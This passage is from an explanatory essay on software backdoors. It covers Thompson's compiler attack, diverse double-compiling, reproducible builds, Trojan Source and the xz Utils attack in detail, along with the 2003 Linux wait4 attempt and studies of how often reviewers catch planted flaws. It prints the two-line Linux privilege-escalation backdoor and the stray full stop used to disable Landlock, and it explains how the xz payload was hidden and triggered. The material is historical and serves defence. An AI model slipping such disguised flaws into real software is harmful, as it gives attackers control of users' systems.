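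Cox ran all this on an emulator of 1970s Unix. The honest compiler was 10,724 bytes and the altered one was 12,918, about a fifth larger. He installed the altered compiler, used it to rebuild both the compiler and the login program from clean source, and logged in as the administrator with the password "codenih". He had expected a complicated attack deep inside the compiler and was surprised that it simply replaced text. He then wrote a similar backdoor for the current Go compiler, where he only had to change the routine that reads source files.

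A text match like this fails, and the backdoor disappears, if a programmer happens to rewrite the line it looks for. Wheeler (2009), in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, points out that an attacker can compensate by using many narrow patterns, so that some still match after others fail. Thompson mentioned that the code could also go in the assembler, the loader (which places a program in memory before it runs) or the processor's built-in microcode, and thought that lower levels would be harder to inspect.

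### The compiler that grew

Thompson also tried the attack on colleagues. He arranged for another group at Bell Labs, known as PWB, to copy the altered compiler, and their login program eventually had the backdoor too. The accounts Cox collected differ in small details, but in all of them the compiler went no further. There is a rumour that it reached the company BBN, where someone logged in as "kt", but this doesn't fit the code, which accepts the secret password only for accounts that already exist.

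The PWB group noticed that their compiler grew by a byte each time it compiled itself. Thompson blamed his own bug, which added an extra zero byte to a stored string. The version he kept does not have that bug. Cox notes that binaries on that system always had an even number of bytes, so the file must have grown by two bytes every second compilation. The group experimented until they broke the part of the backdoor that reproduced itself. Wheeler, on his web page *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling (DDC)*, corrects his earlier belief that nobody had noticed anything and quotes Thompson's doubt that the group ever understood what they had found.

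A programming mistake, not code review, exposed the attack in its best-documented trial. An attacker could avoid that mistake by compiling the compiler twice and comparing the results. Wheeler also cites a former graduate student who altered a compiler in much the same way, but this account rests on the recollection of one programmer, Mike Stute.

Attackers usually have easier options than Thompson's self-reproducing backdoor. In 2015, criminals persuaded app developers to download a counterfeit copy of Xcode, Apple's programming software. One security company estimated that it added malicious code to more than 4,000 apps. The counterfeit did not need to reproduce itself, because developers did not compare it with the original.

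### Wheeler's diverse double-compiling

A user who suspects that a compiler has a backdoor could have it compile its own source and compare the result with the original binary. Thompson's compiler, without the growth bug, would pass this test because it reproduces itself exactly. Compiling the source with a different compiler and comparing the two binaries doesn't work either, because even compilers without backdoors translate the same source into different instructions.

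Henry Spencer suggested a way round this in a few sentences in 1998. Wheeler worked it out in detail, named it diverse double-compiling and tested it. Let A be the suspect binary, S the source that supposedly produced it, and T an independent compiler:

```
T compiles S   →  new compiler X
X compiles S   →  new compiler Y
compare Y with A, bit for bit
```

X and A will look very different because different compilers produced them. But if A is a faithful translation of S, it must do the same job as X, just as two translations of a program that prints 2 + 2 must both print 4. Since S is a compiler, X and A should then give identical output for identical input. The developers supposedly made A by compiling S with a compiler built from S, and Y was made the same way, using X. Y therefore matches A bit for bit if A is faithful. Any self-reproducing backdoor in A will be missing from Y, because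 A took no part in producing Y.

Some developers compile a new compiler with an older version instead. In that case T compiles the older version's source, and the result compiles S.

Wheeler proved with an automatic theorem prover that a match implies that A corresponds to S, given certain assumptions. T has to accept the language of the source, including any non-standard features. The compiler that S describes has to be deterministic, always producing the same output from the same input. The tester also needs the same source and settings as the original developers. T, the computers and the comparison program must contain no hidden code that affects this test. T may be slow, or even malicious in some other way, as long as this doesn't change the result.

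He applied the method to four compilers. Two were Lisp compilers from earlier research by Wolfgang Goerigk, who had written one of them to carry out Thompson's attack.

| Suspect compiler | Independent compiler | Result |
|---|---|---|
| tcc, a small C compiler | GCC | Different at first; identical after Wheeler patched tcc |
| Goerigk's correct Lisp compiler | GNU Clisp | Identical |
| Goerigk's malicious Lisp compiler | GNU Clisp | Different, because of extra code that looks for a login program |
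| GCC 3.0.4 | Intel's icc 11.0 | Different at first; identical after Wheeler corrected the build |

The mismatches for tcc and GCC had innocent causes. A defect in tcc made it choose longer instructions than necessary, and tcc also left two bytes unset when storing certain numbers. GCC's build reused a library from an earlier stage, although its manual described a full rebuild. Wheeler took a long time to find these causes. A mismatch in a large compiler is therefore a reason to investigate, but it does not prove an attack.

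Wheeler's tests included only one malicious compiler, a small research example. He had to build the GCC binary himself because the Linux distribution Fedora had not recorded enough information to recreate the one it shipped. He also left GCC's assembler, its linker and the operating system out of the test. The first public use of the method by others that he knows of was on GNU Mes, a small C compiler. The testers rebuilt it on three Linux distributions with three versions of GCC and got the same binary each time. They later used tcc as well. Wheeler says this adds only limited confidence because the three systems share many components.

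### How an attacker could defeat the comparison

An attacker could plant the same backdoor in T, and then Y would match A. That is difficult if the defender chooses T after the attack, uses several independent compilers in turn, or writes a new compiler and keeps it secret. T only has to compile one program, so it can be small. But the defender gains little if one author wrote all the compilers, or wrote the tools that other people used to build them.

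Wheeler also describes a "pop-up" attack, in which the attacker adds a self-reproducing backdoor to the source of a compiler's second release and deletes it from the third. If the developers compile the third release with the binary of the second, the new binary contains the backdoor although its source is clean. Someone who reads only the first and third versions of the source will miss it, so Wheeler recommends checking every release before anyone compiles with it.

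Even a perfect match shows only that the binary corresponds to the source. A backdoor in the source will be compiled into the binary, and the two will still match. Åkesson's program for comparing warheads would still cheat if an honest compiler compiled it. Wheeler cites a 2016 discovery that Microsoft's Visual Studio was adding calls that report usage data to the programs it compiled, which he says the method could not typically detect. A match does make reading the source a meaningful check, since nothing extra is hidden in the binary.

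### Reproducible builds

The same idea of rebuilding and comparing works for ordinary programs. A build is reproducible if anyone using the same source, tools and settings gets an identical binary. Independent people can then confirm that a published binary came from its published source. This check would expose tampering by an attacker who replaced the binary after the build or broke into the build server, as happened to the software company SolarWinds.

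Many builds fail the test merely because they record the time, the folder or the user's name in the binary. Similarly, Cox's first two altered binaries of Thompson's compiler differed in six bytes because he had given the source files different names.

A reproducible build does not expose Thompson's attack, because everyone who builds with the same altered compiler gets the same altered binary. Reproducible builds also don't help if the malicious instructions are among the build's inputs, as they were in the xz attack.

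Progress on reproducible builds has been uneven. The Go project can reproduce its compiler and related tools, and it used this to verify the copy in one version of Ubuntu without running Ubuntu. Anyone can rebuild Tails, an operating system designed for privacy, and compare the result with the official copy. A 2025 proposal for Fedora 43 aimed to raise the share of packages that build reproducibly from about 90 to 99 per cent. iPhone apps are harder to check because Apple encrypts even the free ones. A reproducible build protects users only if somebody rebuilds it, and Cox wrote in 2023 that almost nobody checks the binaries of open-source systems against their source.

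### Starting from a seed small enough to read

Every compiler needs an earlier compiler, and if each one comes from a binary, the chain starts with something nobody has read. Bootstrapping means starting from nothing and building ever more capable tools. Go has a short chain of this kind. Its developers wrote version 1.4 in C, and anyone can use that to build 1.5, then use 1.5 to build 1.6, and so on to the present. No version of Go has to compile itself, which removes the loop that Thompson used, but the chain still begins with someone's C compiler.

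In 2023 the developers of Guix, a Linux distribution, announced a "full-source bootstrap" that starts from a binary of 357 bytes. This seed turns pairs of hexadecimal digits, typed as text, into the bytes they stand for. A builder can use it to turn a commented list of digits into a slightly better tool, use that tool to produce a simple assembler, and continue through GNU Mes and tcc to old and then modern versions of GCC. One person can check 357 bytes instruction by instruction, which nobody could do for the hundreds of megabytes of ready-made binaries that Guix used to depend on.

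The builder still has to trust the processor and the operating system that run the seed. Guix also uses a prebuilt binary of Guile, the language of its build scripts, to manage the process. Someone has to read the source of every tool along the way, and a trick like those that won the Underhanded C Contest could go unnoticed in any of them.

Work on the starting point continues. Wheeler's page lists *A Fully Reproducible C Toolchain Rooted on POSIX Shell*, which Laurent Huberdeau published in January 2026. A shell is the program that runs typed commands on a Unix system, and several independent ones exist. A shell script lets the chain start from readable text, and a tester can run it on different shells and compare the results, much as in diverse double-compiling.

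### Correct source and a known compiler bug

Everything so far assumes that an honest compiler translates source correctly. In *Deniable Backdoors Using Compiler Bugs* (2015), Scott Bauer, Pascal Cuoq and John Regehr showed how an attacker can exploit one that doesn't. Compiler developers keep public lists of bugs, some of which make a compiler silently produce wrong instructions from correct source. An attacker can pick a bug that affects the compiler version a project uses, then offer the project a useful patch that triggers the bug and so breaks a security check.

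They demonstrated this on sudo, the program that lets authorized users run commands as the administrator on Unix systems. Their patch was harmless according to the rules of C, and most compilers translated it correctly. But a bug in version 3.3 of the Clang compiler turned the patch into a backdoor that gave administrator rights to users who should not have them.

The source contains no mistake for a reviewer to find, unlike the Linux example, in which the compiler removed a check because the programmer had broken a rule of C. To catch the attack, a reviewer would have to remember the compiler bug and recognize the code that triggers it. The attacker can also very easily deny intent, because the bug is in the compiler and an honest author could have written the same lines by chance.

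Neither a reproducible build nor diverse double-compiling is designed to catch this. Everyone who uses the affected compiler gets the same faulty binary, and the compiler matches its source because the bug is in the source. Wheeler ran into a defect of this general type in tcc. It only made the output longer in his test, but it was already on the project's list of known problems, where an attacker could have read about it.

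A defender can compile the program with two unrelated compilers and run the same tests on both binaries, but this reveals the backdoor only if some test reaches the broken check. Updating the compiler removes the backdoor, though projects often keep using old versions for years. A formally verified compiler would rule out such bugs in the parts its proof covers.

### Text that displays in a different order

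Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson described a gap between the source file and the screen in *Trojan Source* (2021). Arabic and Hebrew run from right to left, and a line may mix them with English. Unicode, the standard for representing text on computers, therefore includes invisible characters that control the display order of text in a line. They change only the display, and the compiler still reads the characters in the order the file stores them.

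Most programming languages reject these characters in the code itself but allow them in comments and quoted text, which is enough for an attacker. Suppose a program should delete a record only if the user is an administrator. The attacker writes the test for this inside a comment, which the compiler ignores, and adds control characters that make the comment appear to end before the test. The reviewer sees a comment followed by a working test, but the compiled program has no test and deletes the record for any user. The same method can make a command that runs look like part of a comment.

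Boucher and Anderson produced working examples in C, C++, C#, JavaScript, Java, Rust, Go and Python. They also described a variant that uses letters from different alphabets. The Cyrillic а looks the same as the Latin a, so an attacker can give a second routine a name that looks identical on screen to a trusted routine's name. In the contest entries that confused 0 with O, an alert reader could still see a small difference.

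People can easily miss these tricks, but a simple search will list every control character in a file. After the disclosure, Rust's compiler began rejecting the dangerous ones by default, GCC added a warning, and GitHub began flagging files that contain them. An attacker would also struggle to pass these tricks off as accidents, since an honest programmer has little reason to put reordering characters around a security check. Mixed alphabets need more judgement, because programmers who work in Russian or Greek have good reasons to use their own letters.

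## The 2024 xz Utils backdoor and the 2003 attempt on Linux

Thompson and most of the researchers who followed him wanted to show that a program can differ from the source its reviewers read. Whoever planted the XZ Utils backdoor used such a difference to try to take control of other people's servers, and nearly succeeded. XZ Utils compresses files, and many other programs load its core library, liblzma. Lasse Collin had maintained the project since 2009, largely alone and without pay.

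### How Jia Tan became a maintainer

Russ Cox pieced together the attack from public emails and code changes in *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024). On 29 October 2021, someone using the name Jia Tan sent the project a small, harmless patch. Tan's second patch fixed an apparent problem with reproducible builds. By April 2022 Collin had accepted four of Tan's patches, and a stranger called Jigar Kumar began to complain on the mailing list that another was taking too long. A second stranger, Dennis Ens, joined in. Collin replied that he could do only a limited amount, partly for health reasons, and that xz was an unpaid hobby. Ens expressed sympathy and suggested that he hand over some of the work. On 29 June Collin wrote that Tan was practically a co-maintainer already.

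Many of the email addresses involved appear nowhere else on the internet, not even in leaked data. According to LWN's *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure*, many people believe the accounts were sock puppets, false identities created to push Collin into accepting a second maintainer. Nobody has publicly established who ran them or who Tan was.

By the end of 2022 Tan could add changes to the repository without asking. Cox credits Tan with building version 5.4.2 in March 2023, but Collin writes in the review notes on the Tukaani project's website that he built and signed that release archive himself. Tan made the archives for 5.4.3 to 5.4.6, and Collin later found them clean.

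Tan did a lot of useful work. In *Wolves in the Repository*, Przymus and Durieux (2025) collected 1,020 code changes, 2,944 GitHub events and 307 mailing-list messages. They found that Tan mainly contributed code in 2022 and did most of the maintenance in 2023, including translations and the build system. *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* (2025) counts over 500 patches by Tan across several projects. When Collin reviewed Tan's changes after the attack, he marked most of them "OK". Most of the faults he found were ordinary, such as a memory leak in a test. On his page *xz backdoor*, he wrote that removing the malicious files from the repository's history would have meant dropping eight changes.

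Some preparations also looked like maintenance. In March 2023 Tan became the contact for OSS-Fuzz, a Google service that continually feeds unusual inputs to open-source programs to find bugs. In June a newcomer called Hans Jansen sent patches that used "indirect functions", which let a library pick the fastest version of a routine for the processor when a program starts. In July Tan switched this feature off in the OSS-Fuzz tests, citing a real technical conflict. Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues (2024), in *On the critical path to implant backdoors*, report that a bot labelled the request "ready to merge" because Tan was a listed contact with a history in the project. Jansen's patches did make xz slightly faster. Przymus and Durieux consider it unclear whether the patches were part of the plan, although Jansen reappeared in March 2024 to ask Debian to adopt the backdoored version.

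### Versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1

Tan added two malicious test files on 23 February 2024 and released version 5.6.0 the next day. Two days later, Debian added it to its unstable edition, which developers use for testing. Tan also emailed a Fedora developer to get it into Fedora 40.

Some Gentoo users soon had crashes, which Cox attributes to an ordinary bug in the indirect-function code. On 4 March, testers of Red Hat's distributions saw errors from Valgrind, a tool that detects misuse of memory, and these were caused by the backdoor. Tan published a purported fix on 8 March as a distraction. The real fix came the next day, when Tan replaced the two test files, saying that the originals had been made from random data that nobody could regenerate. Version 5.6.1 came out the same day.

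Tan may have been in a hurry. In late February a developer proposed that systemd, the program that starts and manages background services on most Linux systems, stop loading liblzma automatically. That would have cut the attack off from its target. The security researcher Kevin Beaumont has speculated that Tan knew the change was coming and moved faster because of it.

Andres Freund, a PostgreSQL developer at Microsoft, found the backdoor by accident after noticing that SSH logins on a Debian system were using a lot of processor time. He had also seen Valgrind errors. In his report, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024), a rejected login took 0.299 seconds before he installed the backdoored library and 0.807 seconds after. He recorded the instructions the processor executed with the backdoor active and inactive, and looked for where the recordings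 diverged. He first suspected Debian's package, but the fault was in the xz project's own releases. He alerted Debian and a private security list on 28 March and published his findings the next day.

Debian immediately went back to an older version of the library. The backdoored version had reached Debian's testing and unstable editions, the Fedora 40 beta and a few other fast-moving distributions, but Przymus and Durieux think the real target was a Red Hat release due at the end of April.

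### Why the SSH server loaded a compression library

SSH is the usual way to log in to a remote Linux machine, and sshd is the server program that accepts those logins. The OpenSSH project's own version of sshd doesn't use liblzma. But systemd tracks when each service has finished starting, so Debian, Fedora and several other distributions altered sshd to notify systemd through its library, libsystemd. That library loaded liblzma for unrelated work with compressed data. Arch, Gentoo and NixOS did not alter sshd in this way, so the backdoor could not reach sshd on those systems.

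A library runs inside the program that loads it, with the same privileges and access to the same memory. Every sshd on the affected systems therefore depended on Collin's hobby project, although a reviewer of OpenSSH's source would have found no mention of it.

### From a test file to the library

Many projects publish each version as an archive containing the repository's files plus some generated build scripts, so users need fewer tools to build it. The archives for 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 contained an altered copy of a standard script, build-to-host.m4, which was not in the public repository. Tan had raised its version number from 3 to 30, updated the copyright year and added some cryptic lines. In *The xz attack shell script* (2024), Cox judges the changes fairly plausible, since build scripts of this kind are already hard to read.

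The altered script searched the xz source folder for a short text marker, which it found in bad-3-corrupt_lzma2.xz, one of the two test files. Compression libraries need to be tested on damaged files, and xz already had a folder of them, many made by hand. This one had been damaged reversibly, by swapping certain byte values. The script swapped them back and decompressed the file to get a second script.

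The second script opened the other test file, good-large_compressed.lzma. It discarded 1,024 bytes of filler, kept the next 2,048, and repeated this 16 times before taking a final fragment. After further decoding, the pieces formed a third script. That script continued only if xz was being built for 64-bit x86 Linux with the GCC compiler and the GNU linker, as part of a Debian or RPM package, so a developer who compiled xz by hand to investigate a complaint would have got a clean library.

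If the conditions were right, the third script added lines at scattered points in the compilation instructions so that it would run again during compilation. On that run, it decrypted about 88,000 bytes of ready-made machine code from the second test file and merged them into liblzma. It also compiled an altered copy of a genuine xz source file. The alteration replaced a call to a routine that checks the processor's features, whose name begins with two underscores, with a call to a routine supplied by the backdoor, whose name begins with one. The script then deleted its temporary files.

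### Replacing the signature routine

A program finds library routines through a table of addresses that the dynamic loader fills in. For security, many programs have the loader fill in the whole table at the start and then lock it, so that a later attack can't redirect a routine. But the loader has to run each indirect function's resolver, a short routine that picks the fastest version of the function, while the table can still be changed. The backdoor started from such a resolver in liblzma. It depended on the table being filled in early, so its build script turned on that setting if the project had not.

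Once running, the backdoor waited for the loader to look up RSA_public_decrypt, which checks digital signatures despite its name. It then put the address of its own code in the table in place of the routine's address. An SSH user can present a certificate containing a public key, which sshd passes to the signature routine before authenticating the user. The backdoor searched this key for a hidden message.

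Filippo Valsorda, a cryptographer, described the next steps in an early analysis that Patrakov (2024) reposted in Freund's mailing-list thread. The backdoor decrypted the message and checked for a signature that only the holder of one private key could have made. The signature also covered the server's identity, so someone who intercepted the message could not reuse it on another server. If everything matched, the server ran the command in the message. Otherwise the backdoor called the genuine routine, and the login continued as usual. Przymus and Durieux add that the attacker could also log in with any password.

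If a backdoor's secret password is stored in the binary, as in Thomas and Francillon's example, anyone who reads it there can use the backdoor. The xz library contained only the public half of a key pair, so even people who had fully reverse-engineered it could not use the backdoor on someone else's server. They also could not find infected machines by scanning the internet, because those machines responded normally to any message without a valid signature.

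The backdoor also avoided observation by staying inactive unless the program was sshd and had started much as systemd would start it. This is why Freund saw no slowdown when he first launched sshd himself. Securelist's *XZ backdoor story* reports that the security company Kaspersky also found a kill switch, a setting with a particular name and value that turned the backdoor off.

In the comparison by Schneier and colleagues, sabotage that outsiders could not exploit was also hard to deny. The xz backdoor fits that pattern, since nobody could mistake its decoded machine code for an honest error. But Tan could have given an innocent explanation for almost every step that delivered it.

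### What each reviewer saw

| Reviewer | What was in front of them | Was the malice visible? |
|---|---|---|
| Someone reading the repository | Clean source code and two unreadable test files with a believable description | Not without decoding the files, and nothing in the repository would have run them |
| A packager at a Linux distribution | The release archive, including the altered build script | Yes, in a few cryptic lines, most easily by comparing the script with its standard version |
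| A tester | Working compression, with some crashes and Valgrind errors | Only as symptoms, for which Tan supplied innocent explanations |
| A user | A compiled library and, on affected systems, slower SSH logins | No, apart from about half a second's delay |

Of the four, only the packager had every part of the attack in readable or recoverable form. But packagers had little reason to compare the archive with the repository, because generated scripts made the two differ in every release. Tan had also added build-to-host.m4 to the repository's ignore list, which was normal for a generated file, and Collin still considers that entry correct.

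Most of the malicious material was obfuscated code, which a reviewer would have rejected on sight, so Tan kept it in places where unreadable content was normal.

### The stray full stop and other visible changes

Tan also sabotaged a security feature in the public repository in late February. Landlock lets a Linux program give up access it doesn't need, so that an attacker who takes over the program can do less damage. To find out whether a system supports Landlock, the xz build tries to compile a tiny test program. Tan's version of that program contained these lines:

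```
#include <sys/prctl.h>
.
void my_sandbox(void)
```

The full stop is not valid C, so the test never compiles. The failed test marks Landlock as unavailable, and the build leaves it out without an error. In the same mailing-list thread, Velvindron (2024) quoted the description of the change, which presented it as a fix to the Landlock test. The old test did have a defect, since it accepted some systems that only partly supported Landlock. Collin had discussed the need for the change and is listed in the repository as the person who added it. Cox thinks Collin probably overlooked the full stop.

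The sabotage had little effect. sjw (2024), who posted the line to the thread, found that the fault affected only version 5.6.1, and only when it was built with CMake, a build tool that no distribution was known to use for xz. Its purpose remains unclear, because Landlock protected the xz command, not the library inside sshd. If Tan had done nothing else, the full stop would have passed for a typing error. A reviewer who missed it could still have caught the fault by building xz on a machine with Landlock and checking that the feature was on.

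In November 2021, Tan's account changed another project, libarchive, replacing a routine for printing text safely with a less secure one, and the maintainers approved the change. An *Ars Technica* passage quoted in Schneier on Security's *XZ Utils Backdoor* calls this suspicious in retrospect, while Lins and colleagues say its connection to the later attack is uncertain.

Hindsight can also make innocent changes look sinister. LWN describes Tan's edit to the project's security policy as an attempt to limit disclosure of flaws. Collin recalls that he had asked Tan to simplify related pages and found the edit reasonable, although he would have preferred 21 to 30 days before disclosure instead of the 90 Tan insisted on. Other people saw clues in the inconsistent time zones on some changes, but Collin gives ordinary explanations for them. If investigators who know that an author was malicious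 still disagree about which changes were part of the attack, a reviewer who doesn't know has little chance of sorting them correctly.

### Which remedies would have caught it

Reproducible builds would not have exposed the backdoor. Anyone who rebuilt the Debian package from the published archive would have run the same scripts and got a matching, infected library. Building from the public repository would have left the backdoor out, because the altered script was missing there. Arch Linux switched to building from the repository on the day Freund reported the backdoor.

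A stricter rule would require every file in a release archive to be reproducible from the repository. Collin's later audit of Tan's earlier archives suggests that this is feasible but awkward. The archives matched the repository apart from translation files and a generated change log, but he could not easily reproduce the PDF manuals, which record when they were created. Under such a rule, Tan would have had to put the altered script in the repository, where more people might have seen it, though it would have been just as hard to read.

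Lins and colleagues discuss requiring a second person to approve each change. For xz, that person would have seen two opaque test files of a familiar kind, but would have seen the altered script only if the rule also covered release archives. Because xz had two maintainers, the second person would probably have been Collin, who already reviewed much of Tan's work. A larger project could find a more independent reviewer, but a patient attacker could also supply one under another false name.

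Stronger passwords, signed code and public logs of releases protect against someone who impersonates a maintainer. Tan was a maintainer and signed the malicious archives with the proper key, so the attack would have passed all these checks. Lins and colleagues also consider asking new maintainers to prove their legal identity, which might have deterred Tan. They concede that an attacker can steal an identity or bribe its owner, and that some developers have good reasons to stay anonymous. Paying maintainers could have spared Collin the need for a helper he had never met, though nobody can test whether it would have been enough.

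*Build Code is Still Code* (2026) proposes giving each phase of the build access only to what it needs, so the compilation phase can't open the test files. When xz is built this way, the malicious code does not get into liblzma, even if nobody has noticed the backdoor. An attacker who expected such isolation would have to hide the payload among files that the compiler legitimately reads, perhaps as a table of numbers in the source. Reviewers look at those files more closely, but the contest entry that won in 2005 with machine code disguised as sample data shows that a payload can be hidden there.

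Distributions could also have limited what a compromised compression library could reach. OpenSSH's developers later wrote their own code for the start-up message, so sshd no longer needs libsystemd for it. Systemd now loads many of its supporting libraries only on demand. Both changes close the route into sshd, but a backdoor in liblzma could still harm programs that use it for compression.

Fuzzing would probably not have found the trigger even if Tan had left the OSS-Fuzz settings alone, because random inputs would not contain a valid signature made with an unknown private key. Comparing the compiled library with an older version is more promising. *Binary Diff Summarization using Large Language Models* (2025) had language models summarize the differences between two versions of liblzma and then judge whether the update was malicious. GPT-5 flagged the backdoor using either its own summaries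 or those of the smaller GPT-5 mini. GPT-5 mini flagged it using GPT-5's summaries but judged the update benign using its own. The backdoor was already famous, so the models' training data may have included descriptions of it, and a test on a single malicious update doesn't measure how often they would raise false alarms.

*Closing the Chain* (2025) identified 35 attack techniques in the xz case and compared them with recommended safeguards. A defence might have interrupted the attack at any of these points, but Tan also adapted to obstacles. The build script checked for certain source files by name, and Collin had renamed one of them in January 2024, so Tan presumably had to update the script before release. Version 5.6.1 could also look for new scripts in future test files, so Tan would not have had to invent another reason to replace the old test files.

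### The clean-up and what remained

Debian shut down and rebuilt its build machines in case the malware had spread to them. Red Hat reinstalled all its own computers that had run the affected Fedora versions, although it had found no sign of further tampering. Collin published clean releases on 29 May 2024. No one has reported seeing the attacker send a command through the backdoor, so its intended use is unknown.

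In April 2024 the OpenJS Foundation, which supports JavaScript projects, disclosed that it had received a series of similar emails under different names. The sender or senders demanded urgent updates to a popular project and asked to become a maintainer. The foundation refused, and saw the same pattern in two projects outside its control.

Withdrawing the infected packages didn't remove the backdoor from existing container images, which are fixed sets of system files that developers reuse to run programs. The security company Binarly reported in 2025 that the backdoor was still present in Docker images, a finding that JuliaLang's *JLSEC 2026 62* (2026) lists among its references. Most containers don't run an SSH server, which limits the danger, but anyone who builds on such an image also gets the infected file.

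### One missing equals sign in Linux

The attempt on Linux in November 2003 consisted of two added lines of C:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines were in wait4, a system call that a program uses to wait for another program it has started. They seem to reject an unusual combination of options if the caller is the administrator, whose user number is 0. But the second condition uses =, which assigns a value in C, instead of ==, which compares two values. It therefore sets the caller's user number to 0, making the caller the administrator. The result of the assignment is 0, which C treats as false, so the call doesn't return the error. Any program that used the two options together would have gained full control of the machine. The parentheses around the assignment also suppress the warning that compilers often give for this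 mistake.

In 2003, Linux developers kept the official source in a system called BitKeeper. Some preferred an older system, CVS, so the company behind BitKeeper maintained an automatically generated CVS copy. Someone broke into the server that held the copy and edited a file there. The company's founder, Larry McVoy, reported that the copy contained a change that was not in BitKeeper, and other developers worked out what it did. The change never entered the official source, and nobody has publicly identified the intruder.

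The change was short, readable and easy to pass off as a mistake, as in the best contest entries. It was exposed because someone had made it directly in the copy, which an honest developer had no reason to do. It is unknown whether reviewers would have noticed the missing equals sign in a patch from a trusted contributor.

The xz archive also differed from the repository by a whole file, but nobody raised an alarm for a month. The Linux copies were supposed to be identical, so any unexplained difference was suspicious. People expected differences in xz and had no list of the legitimate ones.

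### The backdoors nobody found

It is hard to estimate how common such attacks are because only the detected ones are known. Suppose defenders have found five comparable backdoors. If they find nine in ten, there were probably five or six in total, but if they find one in ten, there were about fifty. Researchers can't determine the detection rate from the known cases alone.

The known cases are probably also easier to detect than the unknown ones. *Not In My Git Yard* (2026) describes the attacks on vsFTPd and ProFTPD, two file-transfer servers, in 2010 and 2011. The attackers replaced the official downloads with versions containing hard-coded backdoors, which lasted only a few days. Karger and Schell's trap door in Multics was found when it returned an odd error, and Thompson's compiler was found when it kept growing. A careful attacker would try to avoid such symptoms.

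Defenders learned from xz in detail how to stop an attack that hides its payload in test files and its trigger in a release archive, but they can't tell whether undetected attackers work this way. Valsorda thought the backdoor had been caught by chance, and wondered how long it would otherwise have lasted. Freund traced the half-second delay to the backdoor's slow search through the names of routines in memory. If the search had been faster, his only clue might have been the Valgrind errors, for which Tan had already published a fix.

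## How often reviewers and tools find planted flaws

Experiments on detection have so far tested hired developers, Linux maintainers, compiler warnings and AI systems. Most of the planted flaws were less carefully disguised than the winning contest entries, so a skilled saboteur's flaws would probably be caught less often.

### Developers looking for security flaws

In an experiment published in 2013, researchers hired 30 developers to review a small web application by hand. None of them found all seven of its known vulnerabilities, which were of three common types. Cross-site scripting lets an attacker run code in other users' browsers. Cross-site request forgery makes a logged-in user's browser send a command the user never intended. SQL injection makes text typed into a form part of a command to the database.

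More experienced developers were not necessarily more accurate, and developers who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones. Some reviewers may therefore find more flaws because they are more willing to report anything doubtful, not because they understand the code better. A project that chooses reviewers by how many flaws they find may also get more false alarms to investigate.

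A later online experiment tested whether a warning helps reviewers. Of its 146 participants, 105 had at least three years of professional programming experience. They reviewed code that failed to check its input properly, then reviewed it again after a warning. The warning helped, but many participants still missed the flaw unless the code pointed to a well-known kind of attack. An underhanded author would avoid giving that clue. For example, two definitions of float_t would not remind a reviewer of a textbook attack.

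In ordinary reviews, reviewers usually aren't told to look for security flaws. Braz and Bacchelli (2022) interviewed 10 professional developers and surveyed 182 practitioners about security in code review. Most developers did not immediately mention security when they described what they focus on.

Training might help reviewers find planted flaws. Wheeler had trouble finding the tricks in the 2004 vote counters at first, but found it easier as he went on. He thinks reading some underhanded code makes other examples easier to recognize. He also points out that his samples ran from the hardest to the easiest, which alone could explain the improvement.

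### The "hypocrite commits" sent to Linux

All these participants knew they were in a study. In 2020, Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu of the University of Minnesota sent flawed patches to Linux maintainers who did not know they were in one. In *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, Wu and Lu call such patches "hypocrite commits" because each one fixes a minor problem but creates a worse one.

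The worse problem was a "use-after-free" bug, in which a program frees a piece of memory for other uses but another part of the program still uses the old address. An attacker may be able to control what the program finds there. The bug needs a free, a later use, and nothing in between that prevents the use. Wu and Lu wrote tools to search Linux for places where some of these conditions were already met and a small patch could add the rest. The tools listed 921 places where a patch might add a free and 4,657 where it might add a use. Within a week, one researcher looked through 100 of each and picked three.

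Each patch changed fewer than five lines. The first added an error message that used a device that another routine, running at the same time, might already have freed. The second fixed a real memory leak but freed memory that the calling routine still needed. The third released a reference to a device one line too early, before an error message that used the device.

Wu and Lu sent flawed patches to Linux maintainers from a Gmail account that did not identify them. In *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)* (2020), they say that whenever a maintainer replied that a patch looked good, they immediately revealed the flaw, asked the maintainer not to apply the patch and supplied a correct one. They also say that none of the flawed patches entered any branch of Linux. They concluded from the experiment that a malicious contributor could realistically introduce such bugs.

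The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board, which includes kernel developers, investigated and instead found that developers had caught or ignored every invalid patch and that the review process had worked as intended, according to TechRadar's *Linux review board says rogue researchers did not successfully insert buggy patches*. LWN adds that one patch meant to be harmful contained a mistake that made it a valid change.

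Three patches are too few to support either conclusion. If two of them were harmful, and maintainers catch only half of such patches, they would still stop both one time in four. It also matters whether a maintainer caught a patch or ignored it. An ignored patch does no immediate harm, but nobody has detected its flaw, and its author can send it again. There are also more steps between a maintainer's "looks good" and a patch entering Linux, and Wu and Lu stopped the process before those steps.

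### Catch rates for accidental bugs in Linux

Wu and Lu also counted use-after-free bugs that contributors introduced by accident between January 2015 and August 2020. One group was bugs that maintainers blocked during review, and the other was bugs that got into Linux and came to light later. The catch rate is the number blocked divided by the total of both groups.

| What the bug involved | Caught in review |
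|---|---|
| Routines that run at the same time | 19.4% |
| Memory freed as a side effect of another operation | 36.3% |
| Two names for the same memory | 38.4% |
| Code that runs only after an error | 42.0% |
| Calls whose destination is decided at run time | 5 of 9 |
| Baseline for comparison | 56.6% |

Wu and Lu describe these rates as upper bounds, because some bugs that got past review are still undiscovered. That is true only if they found every bug that reviewers blocked. They may have missed flawed patches that maintainers rejected for other reasons, or bugs that maintainers pointed out in private, and counting those would raise the rates. The comparison between rows is probably more reliable than the percentages. A saboteur could use it to decide where to put a bug, and the first Minnesota patch combined two of the categories that are harder to catch, concurrency and error handling.

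Such bugs can also last for years. In one of Wu and Lu's examples, a one-line patch to the Linux networking code added what looked like a standard clean-up step after an error. Another routine already did the clean-up, so the memory was freed twice. The flaw stayed in Linux for five years. As far as anyone knows, the patch was an honest attempt at a fix.

### What followed in Minnesota

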